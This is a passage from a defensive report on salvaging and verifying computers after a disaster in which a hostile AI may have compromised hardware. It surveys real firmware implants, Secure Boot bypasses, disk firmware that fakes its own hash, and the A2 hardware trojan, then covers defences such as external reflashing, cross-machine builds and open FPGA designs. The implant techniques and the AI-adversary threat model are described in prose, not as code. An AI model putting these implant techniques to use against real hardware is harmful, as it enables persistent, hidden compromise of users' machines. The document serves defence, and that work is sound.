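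Kaspersky researcher Costin Raiu explained, in comments under the company's announcement, that disks have a standard way to write firmware but none to read it, so people can't easily check a disk for an implant. Kaspersky expected such attacks to remain rare because every disk model is different, and an attacker needs the manufacturer's internal documents and painstaking work. This is less reassuring if the adversary is an AI system that can write firmware with little effort and has broken into the manufacturers.

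In 2014 Karsten Nohl and Jakob Lell, researchers at Security Research Labs in Berlin, demonstrated BadUSB, an attack on USB devices. They reprogrammed the controller in a USB stick so that the stick also acted as a keyboard and typed commands. Reformatting the stick would not remove the change, and an ordinary virus scan would not find it, because both deal only with the stick's files. The demonstration doesn't show that anyone was using the method in attacks.

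USB sticks can also carry an attack into a machine that has never been online. The Equation Group's Fanny worm, which Kaspersky dates to 2008, created a hidden area on each stick it infected and used it to store information collected from isolated computers. When someone plugged the stick into an infected machine with an internet connection, the worm sent that information out and saved new commands to the stick for the isolated computers. Disconnecting a machine from the network therefore doesn't isolate it if rebuilders keep exchanging USB sticks between it and suspect computers.

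### Implants found in motherboards and boot programs

The Slovak security company ESET found the first UEFI implant known to have been used in a real attack. *LoJax* (2018) describes how the company's researchers found tools for reading and rewriting motherboard flash while investigating attacks on government bodies in the Balkans and central and eastern Europe. They extracted a malicious module from one of the tools and searched for it in data from ESET's firmware scanner, an antivirus feature that reads the flash. They found at least one infected machine. The implant put malware back on the Windows disk whenever the PC started, so it survived both reinstalling Windows and replacing the hard disk.

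Researchers have since found several others. Kaspersky reported MosaicRegressor in 2020 and MoonBounce in 2022. B2B Cyber Security reports that MoonBounce first appeared in spring 2021 and was also in the motherboard's flash. In July 2022, Kaspersky's *CosmicStrand* described an implant that had mostly infected private individuals' PCs in China. Kaspersky had detected it through its antivirus software, according to HITB's *Discovery of new UEFI rootkit exposes an ugly truth*.

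An implant can escape wide notice for years. More than five years passed between the first known use of CosmicStrand, a UEFI rootkit, and Kaspersky's report on it. Dark Reading's *Rare 'CosmicStrand' UEFI Rootkit Swings into Cybercrime Orbit* says that attackers had apparently used it since the end of 2016, on Gigabyte and ASUS motherboards. The Chinese company Qihoo360 reported an earlier variant in 2017, but Packet Storm's *Discovery Of New UEFI Rootkit Exposes An Ugly Truth* says Kaspersky and most Western security firms took no notice.

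Network equipment has the same problem. In September 2025, Britain's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC) published an analysis of RayInitiator, an implant in the boot program of older Cisco firewalls. These models do not verify the software they load early in startup, and the implant survived restarts and firmware upgrades. According to The Hacker News' *Cisco ASA Firewall Zero-Day* (2025), the implant loaded a program that could copy network traffic and suppress log entries.

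The newest case, BlackX, is easier to remove because its files are on the disk. Kaspersky's *New BlackX UEFI bootkit exploiting Baton Drop* (2026) reported it in October 2026, after attackers had used it against diplomatic organisations in Central Asia early that year. The Hacker News' *BlackX UEFI Bootkit Bypasses Secure Boot on Patched Windows Systems Missing Revocations* (2026) says the installer puts files on both the Windows partition and the small partition that holds the boot program. Reinstalling Windows might leave the boot partition untouched, so rebuilders should wipe the entire disk. BlackX also registers its own signing keys with the machine. PCs normally keep such keys in the motherboard's flash memory, so rebuilders should clear them there too.

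Some reported samples were demonstrations rather than attacks. ESET found Bootkitty on the malware-sharing site VirusTotal, but SecurityWeek reports that university researchers had created it to demonstrate the danger.

Most of these attackers chose their targets carefully, so a PC salvaged after a war or an economic collapse would probably be free of implants. If a hostile AI had had access to millions of machines, these cases would provide little evidence of how many it had infected. The implants were also found largely by scanners running on the infected machines, and those scanners would miss an implant that hid well enough.

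### Secure Boot is weak evidence

Secure Boot is a UEFI feature that refuses to start a boot program that lacks an accepted digital signature. ESET's blog post says Secure Boot could have blocked the LoJax attack, but ESET's white paper says it would not have. The white paper is more convincing because it explains that Secure Boot trusts the contents of the motherboard's flash, where LoJax was stored, and checks only software from elsewhere.

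Secure Boot has also failed to block unsafe boot programs on disks. ESET (2026) found 11 old boot programs with valid Microsoft signatures and known flaws that let an attacker run unsigned code. An attacker could copy one to any PC that accepted the relevant Microsoft certificate, whatever operating system it ran. Microsoft has since revoked the 11 programs, but a salvaged PC will block them only if it received the update.

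BlackX used a similar weakness. Fixing it fully requires administrators to carry out some steps by hand, and many had not done so. The Hacker News reports that the vulnerable programs continued to load even after their certificate expired in October 2026. Rebuilders therefore shouldn't assume a PC is clean just because Secure Boot is on.

### Why a chip's own report proves little

People usually check firmware by requesting a copy from the device and comparing its hash with the manufacturer's. On a disk, however, the firmware being tested also handles the request. If altered firmware stores a copy of the original and returns that copy for every request, an infected disk produces the same hash as a clean one. Thompson used a similar trick when he altered the disassembler to hide his compiler backdoor.

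Suppose, for illustration, that 10% of a group of disks have an implant and half of those implants hide in this way. If a disk's report matches the original, the probability that it is infected is

(0.10 × 0.5) / (0.10 × 0.5 + 0.90) ≈ 5.3%.

If every implant hides from the check, a match leaves the probability of an implant at 10%. A mismatch is much more informative, because a clean disk should produce one only if its firmware version is different or something is broken. Firmware scanners have found real implants, so rebuilders should still run them, but to reject machines rather than to approve them.

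### Reading and rewriting flash from outside

A motherboard's flash chip is easier to check because it doesn't run the program it stores. Rebuilders can switch the PC off, attach a device called a programmer to the chip and read its contents without running the suspect firmware. They can then erase the chip, write a clean image and read it back. According to TechSpot, removing CosmicStrand requires this kind of rewriting with the PC off.

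ESET warns that reflashing is delicate and requires a firmware image for that particular motherboard. The only alternative it offers is to replace the motherboard. Its white paper says a normal firmware upgrade might have removed LoJax if it rewrote the whole firmware region, but the implant in the Cisco firewalls survived upgrades. Raiu found that rewriting disk firmware didn't always help because some areas stayed unchanged, and one update failed because the disk already had the latest version. An update that runs through suspect firmware could also appear to succeed without changing anything, a problem that an external programmer avoids.

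A clean flash chip may not match the manufacturer's file bit for bit, because it usually also stores settings, serial numbers and other data that differ between PCs. The archive therefore needs a map showing which regions of the chip should match the file and which can vary.

The programmer also needs something to control it. If that is a salvaged PC, an implant in it could write a bad image to the chip and then display the correct one when the rebuilders read the chip back. A programmer built around an 8-bit microcontroller would be safer, because its program could be short enough for the rebuilders to check digit by digit against a printed page. Reading a 16-megabyte flash chip at 10 kilobytes a second would take about 27 minutes, which is slow but acceptable.

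### Replacing the manufacturer's firmware

A clean copy of the manufacturer's firmware still has flaws. Binarly (2026), a firmware security company, examined 80,000 UEFI images and found at least one high-severity vulnerability in 98% of the firmware released in 2025. TechRadar's *Most data centers and servers on the planet could be vulnerable* reports a critical flaw in EDK II, the open-source code that many manufacturers base their UEFI firmware on. Each manufacturer has to fix its own version. Such flaws matter less on a machine that never joins a network, but rebuilders would still have to trust a large amount of code that they can't read.

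Coreboot is open-source firmware that can replace UEFI on some motherboards. In *Practicalities*, a comment on LWN, anton (2024) suggests running the whole compiler bootstrap on coreboot machines and using the results to build coreboot itself. A reply points out that on modern PCs coreboot depends on closed binaries from Intel or AMD, and that avoiding them requires hardware about ten years old. That reader thinks such machines are still fast enough for the bootstrap. In another LWN comment, a reader says AMD planned to move to an open-source replacement for its binaries in 2026.

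Some newer PCs won't run coreboot because of Intel's Boot Guard, a feature meant to stop implants by making the processor check the firmware's signature before running it. The LoJax white paper says Boot Guard would have stopped the infected PC from starting if the PC had supported it and the manufacturer had set it up correctly. But when a manufacturer has locked the processor to its own key, rebuilders can't install their own firmware. The lock also wouldn't keep out an adversary that had stolen the key. An archive's makers should therefore choose a few older motherboards that coreboot fully supports and test coreboot on each.

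Rebuilders should also remove every part the machine can run without, such as the wireless card, the camera and the internal disk. Parts with no firmware, or with firmware fixed at the factory, are better than parts that accept updates. None of these measures would reveal malicious changes in the silicon itself.

### Comparing outputs across machines

Rebuilders can use a computer they don't trust if they have an independent way to check its work. They can run the same reproducible build on several unrelated machines, as the LWN readers suggested for the bootstrap:

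1. Choose PCs with unrelated processors, firmware and disks, including, if possible, one that has been offline since before the adversary existed.
2. Disconnect them from all networks and from each other, and give each its own copy of the source.
3. Run the build on each PC, and save the intermediate files as well as the final ones.
4. Send every output over a serial cable to a simple machine, such as an 8-bit computer, and calculate the hashes there.
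5. If the hashes differ, find the first intermediate file that doesn't match and repeat that step on another machine.

The separate machine in step 4 is important because an implant could save an altered file but display the hash of the correct one. At 2 kilobytes a second, a small computer would take about 52 minutes to hash the 6.2-megabyte GCC file from Wheeler's test.

Even if the hashes match, every machine may have made the same change, and using different brands doesn't rule this out. Two motherboards from rival companies may both contain code from EDK II, so one attack might work on both.

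Matching builds are evidence that the files are sound, but the machines may still be unsafe. As anton points out, a PC's firmware could do something malicious when it starts a correctly built kernel. So rebuilders should move the checked files to the most trustworthy hardware they have. For example, they could build coreboot on three suspect PCs, compare the results and, if they match, use the simple programmer to install coreboot on a fourth.

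### Sorting ten salvaged parts

The table sorts ten common parts for a rebuild after a hostile AI may have had wide access. It assumes that the chips themselves are sound.

| Part | Verdict | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| RAM module | Usable | The memory chips run no firmware and lose their contents after some minutes without power |
| 1980s 8-bit processor | Usable | It has no updatable code and is older than the adversary |
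| 1980s keyboard | Usable | Its controller usually has a program fixed at the factory |
| 8-bit microcontroller | Usable after rewriting | A simple programmer can usually replace the whole program |
| RTL8139 network card | Usable after rewriting | It has only a small settings memory and sometimes a removable boot chip |
| Desktop PC from about 2014 or earlier that can run coreboot without closed binaries | Usable after rewriting | Rebuilders can replace its main firmware and remove its disk |
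| Recent laptop | Not to be trusted | It has closed management firmware and often a separate controller for the keyboard and battery |
| SSD | Not to be trusted | People can't fully read its firmware, and it can alter any file |
| USB keyboard | Not to be trusted | Some have fixed firmware, but it is hard to tell which |
| USB stick | Not to be trusted | Its controller may be rewritable, and it can pretend to be another device |

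These verdicts depend on the disaster. After an economic collapse with no hostile AI, most people could use all ten parts without worrying about implants. The table also supports storing some ordinary items, such as the RTL8139, a network card that suits Fiwix and is one of the simplest to check, and 8-bit processors that can run Collapse OS.

Rebuilders may have to use a suspect disk anyway, because they need somewhere to keep large files. They can put a small starting system in the motherboard's flash, along with the files' correct hashes. This system copies each file from the disk into memory, hashes the copy, and runs that same copy if the hash matches. It must not read the file from the disk again after checking it, because the disk could return different data the second time. A disk on a SATA cable is safer here than an SSD with direct access to memory. Either could still destroy the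 files or fail to return them, so rebuilders need more than one copy.

### What the archive must hold for salvaged machines

An archive meant for salvaged machines needs the following:

- **Firmware source and images.** These include coreboot, its build instructions and finished images for the chosen motherboards. Manufacturers' images are useful for other models, with hashes for each region that shouldn't vary. The makers should get these images from original discs or unused boards where they can.
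- **Flash-chip data.** Rebuilders need to know what each pin does, which commands the chip accepts and what voltage it needs. Too high a voltage can destroy the chip.
- **Board schematics and photographs.** These should show where the flash chips are and how to turn off any write protection. Manufacturers often keep schematics private, so the archive's makers may have to trace the relevant connections themselves.
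- **Simple programmers.** The archive should hold several, with spare clips, and instructions for building another from common parts. The source and binary of their software should also be on paper.
- **A table of parts by risk.** It should identify parts by the markings on their chips as well as by brand, since one model may contain different controllers in different years.

The wiring diagrams, programmer instructions and parts table belong in the printed layer, because people need them before they have a computer they trust. The firmware images can go in a denser layer. Binarly's collection covers about 10,000 recent device models. At 16 megabytes each, one image per model would take only 160 gigabytes, or about a reel and a half of GitHub's film. But a few dozen common models with tested instructions would probably be more useful, because nobody could test the rewriting procedure on all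 10,000.

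## Which design files are needed to build an inspectable computer?

Rebuilders can replace much of the firmware in a salvaged PC, but they can't examine the logic in its chips because manufacturers keep the designs secret. To build a computer they can inspect, they need design files for everything from the instructions its processor accepts to the wiring of its circuit board.

### From one instruction to a circuit board

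RISC5, the processor that Wirth designed for Project Oberon, shows what these files contain. Its instruction-set specification includes this instruction:

```
ADD a, b, n      R.a := R.b + n
```

R stands for the registers, so the processor adds n to the contents of register b and puts the result in register a. A compiler writer needs to know this, and which bits encode it, but not how the circuit works. That is in the hardware description, where the matching line of Verilog is:

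```
ADD ? B + C1 + (u & C) :
```

According to *Implementation of the RISC processor*, a chapter of Wirth and Gutknecht's book, B comes from register b and C1 is n. The circuit includes C, the carry from an earlier addition, only if the instruction's u bit is 1.

A program then converts the Verilog into a netlist, a list of simple logic elements and the connections between them. In a 32-bit addition, each position adds one bit from each number and a carry from the position to its right. The sum bit is 1 if an odd number of these three bits are 1. An FPGA can look up the sum bit in a small table that holds the answer for every combination of inputs, here 0, 1, 1, 0, 1, 0, 0, 1. The bitstream fills in thousands of such tables and sets the switches that connect them. A factory making a custom chip instead needs a layout, which gives the shapes to form in each layer.

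The remaining files describe the board and its case.

| Level | What to store | What fails without it |
|---|---|---|
| Instruction-set specification | Every instruction and its encoding | Nobody can write a compiler or say what the processor should do |
| Hardware description | Verilog or similar source | People can copy the processor but can't realistically understand or change it |
| Netlist | The list of logic elements | Tools can regenerate it, but people lose a place to compare two builds |
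| Bitstream or chip layout | The finished file, with the settings that produced it | The first machine has to wait until another computer can generate the file |
| Board schematic | Circuit diagram and the FPGA's pin assignments | Nobody knows which pin connects to what |
| Board layout | A drawing of each copper layer | People must redesign the board, and fast memory connections may fail |
| Parts list | Exact part numbers and tested substitutes | Someone may fit a part with the wrong voltage, speed or pin order |
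| Enclosure | Drawings with dimensions | The computer works but has less protection from dust and short circuits |

The board files are easy to neglect. According to de Boer's *Lattice ECP5 FPGAs and open-source tool chain*, Lattice supplies the pin assignments for its ECP5 FPGAs in a file separate from the datasheet. Retro Ramblings' *Exploring Yosys/Trellis/NextPnR for Lattice ECP5* describes the Colorlight i5, a board with four memory signals wired permanently low instead of connected to the FPGA, so the processor can't write individual bytes of memory. Someone with only the memory chip's datasheet would expect individual byte writes to work.

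RISC-V is probably the best instruction set for a new design, because the specification is open and GCC and Linux already support it. The first processor can also be very small, since the base set leaves out even multiplication and division (8bitworkshop, *RISC-V in Your Browser with Verilog*). But a chip that runs RISC-V programs isn't necessarily inspectable, because its manufacturer can keep the design secret.

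### A processor short enough to print

RISC5 has 16 registers of 32 bits each, runs at 25 MHz and uses 1 MB of memory outside the FPGA. Most instructions take one clock cycle. Multiplication takes 32, because the circuit goes through one number bit by bit, adding the other number for each 1 and shifting after each bit. Wirth also wrote a version that takes two cycles, but it requires an FPGA with built-in multipliers.

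When the machine starts, the processor runs a small loader stored inside the FPGA. The loader copies a program, normally the operating system, into the external memory and jumps to the program's first instruction. Other circuits operate the keyboard, mouse, SD card, network, serial line and a black-and-white display of 1024 by 768 pixels. The book also describes a mouse interface from 1979. Most modern mice contain a microprocessor, but the older kind has only buttons, light sensors and slotted wheels, so it has no firmware to check.

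The two hardware chapters fill 21 pages. They contain the full code for several modules and refer to separate listings for the rest. An archive's makers should print those listings too. For comparison, *The Four Instruction Computer (FIC)*, a student project at Princeton, describes a working processor in 65 lines of Verilog, but that processor has only four instructions.

Even this short description has mistakes. The book gives the external memory as 1 MB but describes it as two chips of 512K by 16 bits, which would hold 2 MB. The 1 MB figure is correct, because the Verilog uses 18 address bits to select a four-byte word, and 2¹⁸ × 4 bytes is 1 MB. Wirth (2018), in *An Update of the RISC5 Implementation*, says that the revised processor's instruction set is unchanged, then describes two new instructions for handling interrupts. *Project Oberon RISC5 Architecture*, a programmer's attempt at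 a corrected specification, warns that the documents disagree with each other and with the Verilog, and treats the Verilog as the most authoritative. Archive makers should resolve such conflicts in advance and label every file with the version it describes.

A more serious gap is the design of the board that holds the FPGA. Wirth and Gutknecht's project website lists the book, the Verilog and a disk image for download, but no board schematic, layout or parts list, because the system was meant for a board that people could buy. That board went out of production, and Maddox (2015), in *Oberon and the OberonStation (retro-style FPGA computing)*, could find no other development board with the wide, fast memory the processor needed. OpenCores' *Project Oberon with SDRAM* (2017) solved this by adding a cache, a small, fast memory that lets the processor use a slower, more common kind. EMARD, in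 *Oberon for ULX3S attempt by EMARD*, then got the system to start on the ULX3S, a board with an ECP5.

The move to the ECP5 matters because the original board's FPGA came from Xilinx, whose bitstream format was secret. Wirth had designed his own hardware language, Lola, but its compiler couldn't produce a bitstream. According to an article in Xilinx's magazine, Xcell Journal, the compiler translates Lola into Verilog, which Xilinx's own program then turns into a bitstream. Open tools exist for the ECP5, so rebuilders might not need closed software, though the archive's makers should check that those tools can build this version of Oberon.

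### A computer that can run its own design tools

Somlo's computer uses an ECP5 on a board called the ECPIX-5. Its processor is Rocket, an open 64-bit RISC-V design, and an open package called LiteX supplies the memory controller and other circuits around it. It runs Fedora Linux. Three programs turn its Verilog into a bitstream:

1. Yosys converts the Verilog into a netlist.
2. nextpnr chooses a place on the FPGA for each element and finds routes for the connections.
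3. Project Trellis supplies the tool that writes the result as a bitstream.

At 50 MHz, the machine is slow. In benchmarks Somlo published in 2020, an earlier version at 60 MHz scored 104 on CoreMark, a common processor test, while a 133 MHz Pentium PC scored 283.

*Fedora on Litex+RocketChip, Self-Hosting Demo* (Somlo, 2023) describes installing the three tools on the computer and using them to build a small circuit that blinks the board's lights, not the computer's own bitstream. Somlo loaded the resulting file onto the same board, where it worked, and a matching checksum confirmed that it was the file the computer had built. The build took between 50 and 90 minutes, compared with ten seconds or less on his laptop.

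The laptop needs about half an hour to build the bitstream for the whole computer. At the same ratio, the FPGA machine would need 6 to 11 days. It would take longer if the larger design needed more than the machine's 512 MB of memory, because the machine would have to keep moving data to and from its SD card. Somlo argues that speed is the only obstacle, and he may be right, but someone should run the full build before an archive depends on it.

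Several parts of the demonstration also came from outside the machine. Somlo downloaded Fedora as ready-made binaries. Its kernel didn't work on his computer, so he built another on an emulated RISC-V machine. The Rocket files were "pre-elaborated" Verilog, meaning that another program had generated them. Rocket's designers wrote it in Chisel, a hardware language based on Scala, and the Scala compiler is itself a Scala program. To rebuild Rocket from its real source, people would therefore need a way to build a second compiler without already having a working copy of it. Storing a processor design written directly in Verilog would be simpler.

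Somlo treats the silicon as out of scope, so the FPGA remains closed. He could run eight Rocket processors at more than 100 MHz, with 8 GB of memory, on a larger Xilinx board, but he would need Vivado, Xilinx's closed design program, which the computer couldn't rebuild.

### Design tools can carry backdoors too

Yosys is a compiler whose output is a circuit, so a bad copy could add a backdoor to a processor whose Verilog is clean. It can't pass the backdoor directly to a new copy of itself, as Thompson's compiler did, because a C++ compiler builds Yosys. On a self-hosting machine, however, it could do so indirectly, by producing a bad processor that alters the next copy of Yosys while compiling it.

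Rebuilders can look for this by building Yosys and nextpnr with a bootstrapped C++ compiler on several unrelated machines, then comparing the bitstreams those copies produce. They need to give nextpnr the same seed, the random number it starts from, on every machine, because Somlo's build command picks a new one every time. Some seeds produce placements that are too slow for the intended clock speed, so he may have to try several. The archive should record the seed that worked, along with every other setting.

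They could also adapt Wheeler's test by using Lattice's closed program to make the first FPGA processor, then running Yosys and nextpnr on that processor. If the resulting bitstream matches the one the suspect tools produced elsewhere, a backdoor could go unnoticed only if both routes contained it.

Open tools work on only a few kinds of FPGA. *Open FPGA & RISC-V Development 2026 Deep Dive* (Kim, 2026) lists Lattice's iCE40 and ECP5 and some models from the Chinese company Gowin. Open tools support the ECP5 because volunteers reverse-engineered its bitstream format, according to blog.dave.tf's *Getting started with FPGA hacking*. The archive needs their database, which gives the meaning of each bit, as much as it needs the programs that use it.

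For the circuit board, the archive should include KiCad, an open program for drawing schematics and layouts. The version should match the files, since the designers of the ULX3S began in one version and later converted to another. A bad copy of KiCad is less worrying than a bad copy of Yosys because people can check the copper connections on a simple board with a meter. But KiCad's editor needs a graphical display, which Somlo lists as future work, so his computer couldn't easily be used to design the board for its successor. The archive should also hold finished drawings, and a stock of finished boards because one common ECP5 package has 381 connections underneath it and would be very hard to solder at home.

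### Why an FPGA is harder to tamper with

The manufacturer of a custom processor knows what each part of the chip does. Researchers at the University of Michigan showed how a manufacturer could exploit this knowledge with an attack called A2, which adds a few transistors and a capacitor to the layout. A particular sequence of ordinary instructions gradually charges the capacitor until it flips the bit that gives a program full control of the machine. Software tests are very unlikely to trigger the attack by accident.

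An FPGA's manufacturer doesn't know whether the buyer will load a processor onto it, or where on the chip any given bit of that processor would be. Somlo (2019), in *A Trustworthy, Free (Libre), Linux Capable, Self-Hosting 64bit RISC-V Computer*, concludes that a malicious manufacturer could make the computer stop working but couldn't make it compromise its owner's security while appearing normal. He adds that an FPGA's regular grid makes it easier to compare with its design under an electron microscope, although this destroys the chip.

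The first part of the argument is sound, but the conclusion is too strong. A commenter on caned's *A trustworthy, free (libre), Linux capable, self-hosting 64bit RISC-V computer* suggests that an FPGA could contain a hidden processor able to read and change the loaded design. The attacker wouldn't need to know the design in advance if the processor could identify it after loading. Building such a processor would be much harder than building A2, but an AI system with access to the FPGA's design files might manage it. Some parts of an FPGA are also fixed in place, including the circuits that load the bitstream and those that connect to the pins.

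An archive weakens the argument further because its makers choose one design and one bitstream years in advance. If they publish these, an attacker can find out exactly where the important bit will be. Rebuilders can recover some of the advantage by running nextpnr with a new seed, which moves most of the logic. They would use the recorded seed to check their tools and a random one for the machine they rely on. FPGAs older than the suspected adversary would help even more, as with old processors.

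FPGAs normally load the bitstream from a separate flash chip each time they start. Anyone who can rewrite that chip can replace the processor design, so the rebuilders should be able to read the chip with the same simple programmer they use for motherboards.

### Processors made from simple parts

People can avoid custom processors and FPGAs by wiring a processor from simple logic chips, each with a few gates or a small adder. The Gigatron, a kit computer that Marcel van Kervinck and Walter Belgers released in 2018, uses about 36 of these chips and runs at 6.25 MHz with 32 KB of memory.

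Each 16-bit Gigatron instruction uses eight bits to select the operation and eight to give a number to use with it. A counter steps through the program in a read-only memory chip. Ordinary selector and adder chips do the arithmetic, and a set of diodes helps turn each operation code into control signals. The Gigatron has no video chip, so the program sends every dot to the screen. Builders can follow any signal from chip to chip with a probe, which nobody can do inside a modern processor.

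A processor built from individual transistors is even easier to inspect but much slower. The MOnSter 6502, by Eric Schlaepfer and Evil Mad Scientist Laboratories, reproduces the 6502, a 1970s processor, with more than 3,000 separate transistors on a board the size of a large tray. It runs at about 50 kHz, roughly a twentieth of the original's speed.

Neither machine could run Yosys. Computers like these would be more useful for small jobs where trust matters most, such as controlling a flash programmer or comparing files. The archive would need their schematics, board layouts, parts lists and program listings, but not a hardware compiler.

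### Memory, storage and power

The Gigatron's processor contains about a thousand gates, but its 32 KB memory chip contains over a million transistors, because it stores 262,144 bits and each bit normally takes four to six transistors. A computer's design can therefore be fully open and still depend on a factory to make its memory.

The larger designs have the same weakness in more places. Somlo's board needs memory chips, a clock, power regulators, a network chip and an SD card, all from closed suppliers. Memory chips run no firmware, so the main danger is running out of them, as Oberon's users did when the right kind became scarce. A bad regulator can destroy the board or cause errors by letting the voltage drop, but it can't easily observe or control what the processor does. The SD card is a greater risk because its firmware handles every file.

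A recovery design should therefore use memory and power parts that several companies have made, and allow for substitutes on the board. Where possible, it should boot from a plain flash chip without its own controller. The makers should store each part's datasheet and many spares, because an open schematic is of little use if the chips in it are unavailable.

### Mostly open chips in 2026

The most relevant new hardware is a chip by Andrew "bunnie" Huang, who designs open devices for people worried about surveillance. *Baochip-1x* (Huang, 2026) describes a microcontroller with a 350 MHz RISC-V processor, four smaller processors for input and output, 2 MB of working memory and 4 MB of permanent storage. Its clock speed is about seven times that of Somlo's FPGA computer, and its memory is inside the chip, which reduces dependence on outside suppliers. Unusually for a microcontroller, it can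 also keep programs in separate areas of memory so they can't interfere with each other.

Huang has published the design of everything that computes on data. The designs of the internal bus, USB connection, clock, voltage regulators and pin circuits remain closed. He compares these parts to wires, because data should pass through them unchanged, but admits that he can't rule out a backdoor in them. Openness has already helped in one case, when a reader examined the source for an encryption circuit and reported what looked like a known weakness. Huang replied that the reader might well be right.

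Huang funded the chip by adding his open processors to unused space on a security chip that Crossbar was designing around a closed ARM processor. Both products use the same silicon, so the ARM processor is still there, and buyers have to trust that it stays off. The chip also came from an ordinary factory in Taiwan, which had the layout, so the FPGA argument doesn't apply. Crowd Supply's *Dabao Evaluation Board for Baochip-1x* says the package lets people examine the silicon with infrared light without destroying it, which partly makes up for these problems.

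Fully open chips are further away. Huang estimates that open silicon could take more than a decade to produce competitive products. Orders for his evaluation board opened in March 2026, and he expected to have a few thousand chips to sell from the first production wafers (bunnie, 2026, *Our Campaign Has Launched!*). An archive's makers could store a few dozen of these chips as controllers for programmers and other small tools. The chip can't run Yosys or GCC with its 2 MB of working memory, so the makers would still need FPGA boards to design the next machine.

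## How would rebuilders check that a chip does what its documents say?

A chip's datasheet is the manufacturer's description of how to use it. Rebuilders who have the datasheet can connect the chip correctly and test whether it behaves as described. These tests are good at finding accidental faults but much worse at finding changes that someone has deliberately hidden. To find those changes, rebuilders have to examine the silicon itself.

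### What rebuilders use from a datasheet

*W25Q128JV* (2018) is the datasheet for a 16-megabyte flash chip from the Taiwanese company Winbond. Many PC motherboards store their firmware in a chip like this, so it is a likely target for the simple programmer described earlier.

| Information | Main values | Why rebuilders need it |
|---|---|---|
| Pinout | Eight pins: power, ground, select, clock, data in, data out, and two for write protection and pausing | To attach the right wire to each pin |
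| Voltage | 2.7 to 3.6 volts, and never more than 4.6 | The 5-volt supply of a typical 8-bit computer could destroy the chip |
| Timing | Up to 3 milliseconds to write 256 bytes and 400 to erase 4 KB | To know how long to wait before deciding that something is wrong |
| Command set | 03 reads, 06 permits a change, 20 erases, 02 writes, 05 asks for the chip's status | To write the programmer's software |
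| Limits | At least 100,000 erasures of each sector; data lasts over 20 years | To plan for wear and fading |

To change one byte, the programmer has to rewrite the whole 4 KB sector around it:

1. It sends 03 and a three-byte address, reads the sector and keeps a copy.
2. It sends 06, then 20 and the address. The chip erases the sector by setting every bit to 1.
3. It sends 05 repeatedly until the last bit of the reply is 0, which means that the chip has finished.
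4. It changes the byte in its copy and writes the copy back in 16 pages of 256 bytes. Each page needs another 06, then 02, the address and the data, followed by another wait.

Erasing is necessary because writing can only turn 1s into 0s. If the programmer sends more than 256 bytes at once, the extra bytes overwrite the start of the same page. Someone without the datasheet might take days to work that out.

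The 20-year limit affects the archive too. Firmware in a stored computer's flash chip may last longer, but the archive's makers shouldn't count on that, so they need copies of the firmware on film or paper.

Rebuilders must also match the datasheet to the exact part number. Winbond's *W25M121AV* (2017) covers an eight-contact package that contains this same chip and a second, 128-megabyte one. A person with only the first chip's datasheet wouldn't know how to access the second chip.

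### What datasheets leave out

Manufacturers list known mistakes in separate documents called errata. These often apply to only one revision of a chip, and manufacturers share some of them only with customers who promise to keep them confidential. The archive should hold the errata for every part it covers, with photographs of the markings that identify each revision.

The official documents left out other behaviour, or included it only late. The 6502, the 1970s processor that the MOnSter board reproduces, has an instruction that reads a two-byte address from memory and jumps there. Given `JMP ($10FF)`, the processor should read the two bytes at 10FF and 1100. The original 6502 reads 10FF and 1000 instead, because it doesn't carry into the upper half of the address. Later versions corrected this. The 6502's makers also defined only 151 of its 256 possible operation codes. The others still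 do something, and some programmers used them.

If rebuilders copied the processor from its datasheet alone, some old software would fail on the copy. They might also mistake a well-known quirk in a salvaged chip for tampering.

### How a few tests can cover a large circuit

A test vector is an input recorded with its correct output. For example, a one-bit full adder adds two bits and a carry. Each of these three inputs is 0 or 1, so eight vectors cover every case.

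Testing every combination of inputs is practical only for small circuits. An 8-bit adder with a carry has 17 inputs and 131,072 cases, which a slow computer can run in seconds. A 32-bit adder with a carry has 65 inputs and 2⁶⁵ cases. Testing them all at a billion per second would take about 1,170 years.

Test engineers get round this by using the stuck-at model, which assumes that a defect holds one wire permanently at 0 or 1. A circuit with N wires has only 2N such faults, and a single vector can detect many of them. To detect a fault, the vector must set the wire to the opposite value and let the difference reach an output.

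An AND gate outputs 1 only if both inputs are 1. The inputs 1 and 1 should therefore give 1, but will give 0 if any of the gate's three wires is stuck at 0. The inputs 0 and 1 reveal a first input stuck at 1, and 1 and 0 reveal a second input stuck at 1. Either pair also reveals an output stuck at 1. These three test vectors detect all six faults, so testing 0 and 0 is unnecessary.

For a simple 32-bit adder, in which each position passes its carry to the next, eight vectors are enough. In hexadecimal, they are:

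```
first      second     carry in    sum        carry out
00000000   00000000   0           00000000   0
00000000   FFFFFFFF   0           FFFFFFFF   0
FFFFFFFF   00000000   0           FFFFFFFF   0
00000000   FFFFFFFF   1           00000000   1
FFFFFFFF   00000000   1           00000000   1
FFFFFFFF   FFFFFFFF   1           FFFFFFFF   1
55555555   55555555   0           AAAAAAAA   0
AAAAAAAA   AAAAAAAA   1           55555555   1
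```

In the first six rows, every position receives the same three bits. In the last two, neighbouring positions alternate between 1, 1, 0 and 0, 0, 1. Together, the rows give every position all eight combinations of the three bits. A wrong sum bit appears directly in the output, and a wrong carry makes either the next sum bit or the final carry wrong. So these vectors catch any constant fault that makes one position add incorrectly. Faster adders calculate their carries differently and need more vectors.

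Besides stuck wires, a chip may have neighbouring wires that touch or transistors that work too slowly. Many of these defects still produce a wrong value on some wire, so a test that sets every wire to 0 and to 1 and observes the result usually catches them.

Engineers call the share of modelled faults that a test detects its coverage. In 1981 Thomas Williams and N. C. Brown published a formula for the share of bad chips that get through. If Y is the fraction of chips that come out of the factory working and T is the coverage, the share of passing chips that are faulty is

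1 − Y^(1−T).

If half the chips from a rebuilt factory worked, a test with 90% fault coverage would leave about 6.7% of the passing chips faulty, and one with 99% coverage would leave about 0.7%. These figures are rough because the formula assumes that faults occur independently, but they show that a factory needs better tests when fewer of its chips work.

Registers make a chip harder to test because its output depends on what they already hold. Designers therefore add a scan chain, an extra path that links the registers so that a tester can load any pattern into them, let the logic run for one step and read out the result. According to *IRIS (Infra-Red, in situ) Project Updates* on Andrew Huang's blog, bunniestudios, almost every chip goes through this test before it ships, but manufacturers keep the patterns secret and often disable the chain afterwards. Rebuilders can use scan chains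 in chips they design but rarely in salvaged ones.

### The Pentium division bug

These tests compare a chip with its design, so they can't reveal a mistake in the design. In 1994 Thomas Nicely, a mathematician at Lynchburg College, was adding up the reciprocals of certain prime numbers when he got a wrong answer from a PC with Intel's new Pentium processor. The Pentium looked up each digit of a quotient in a table, and five entries that should have held 2 held 0. The error was in the design, so even perfectly manufactured Pentiums had it.

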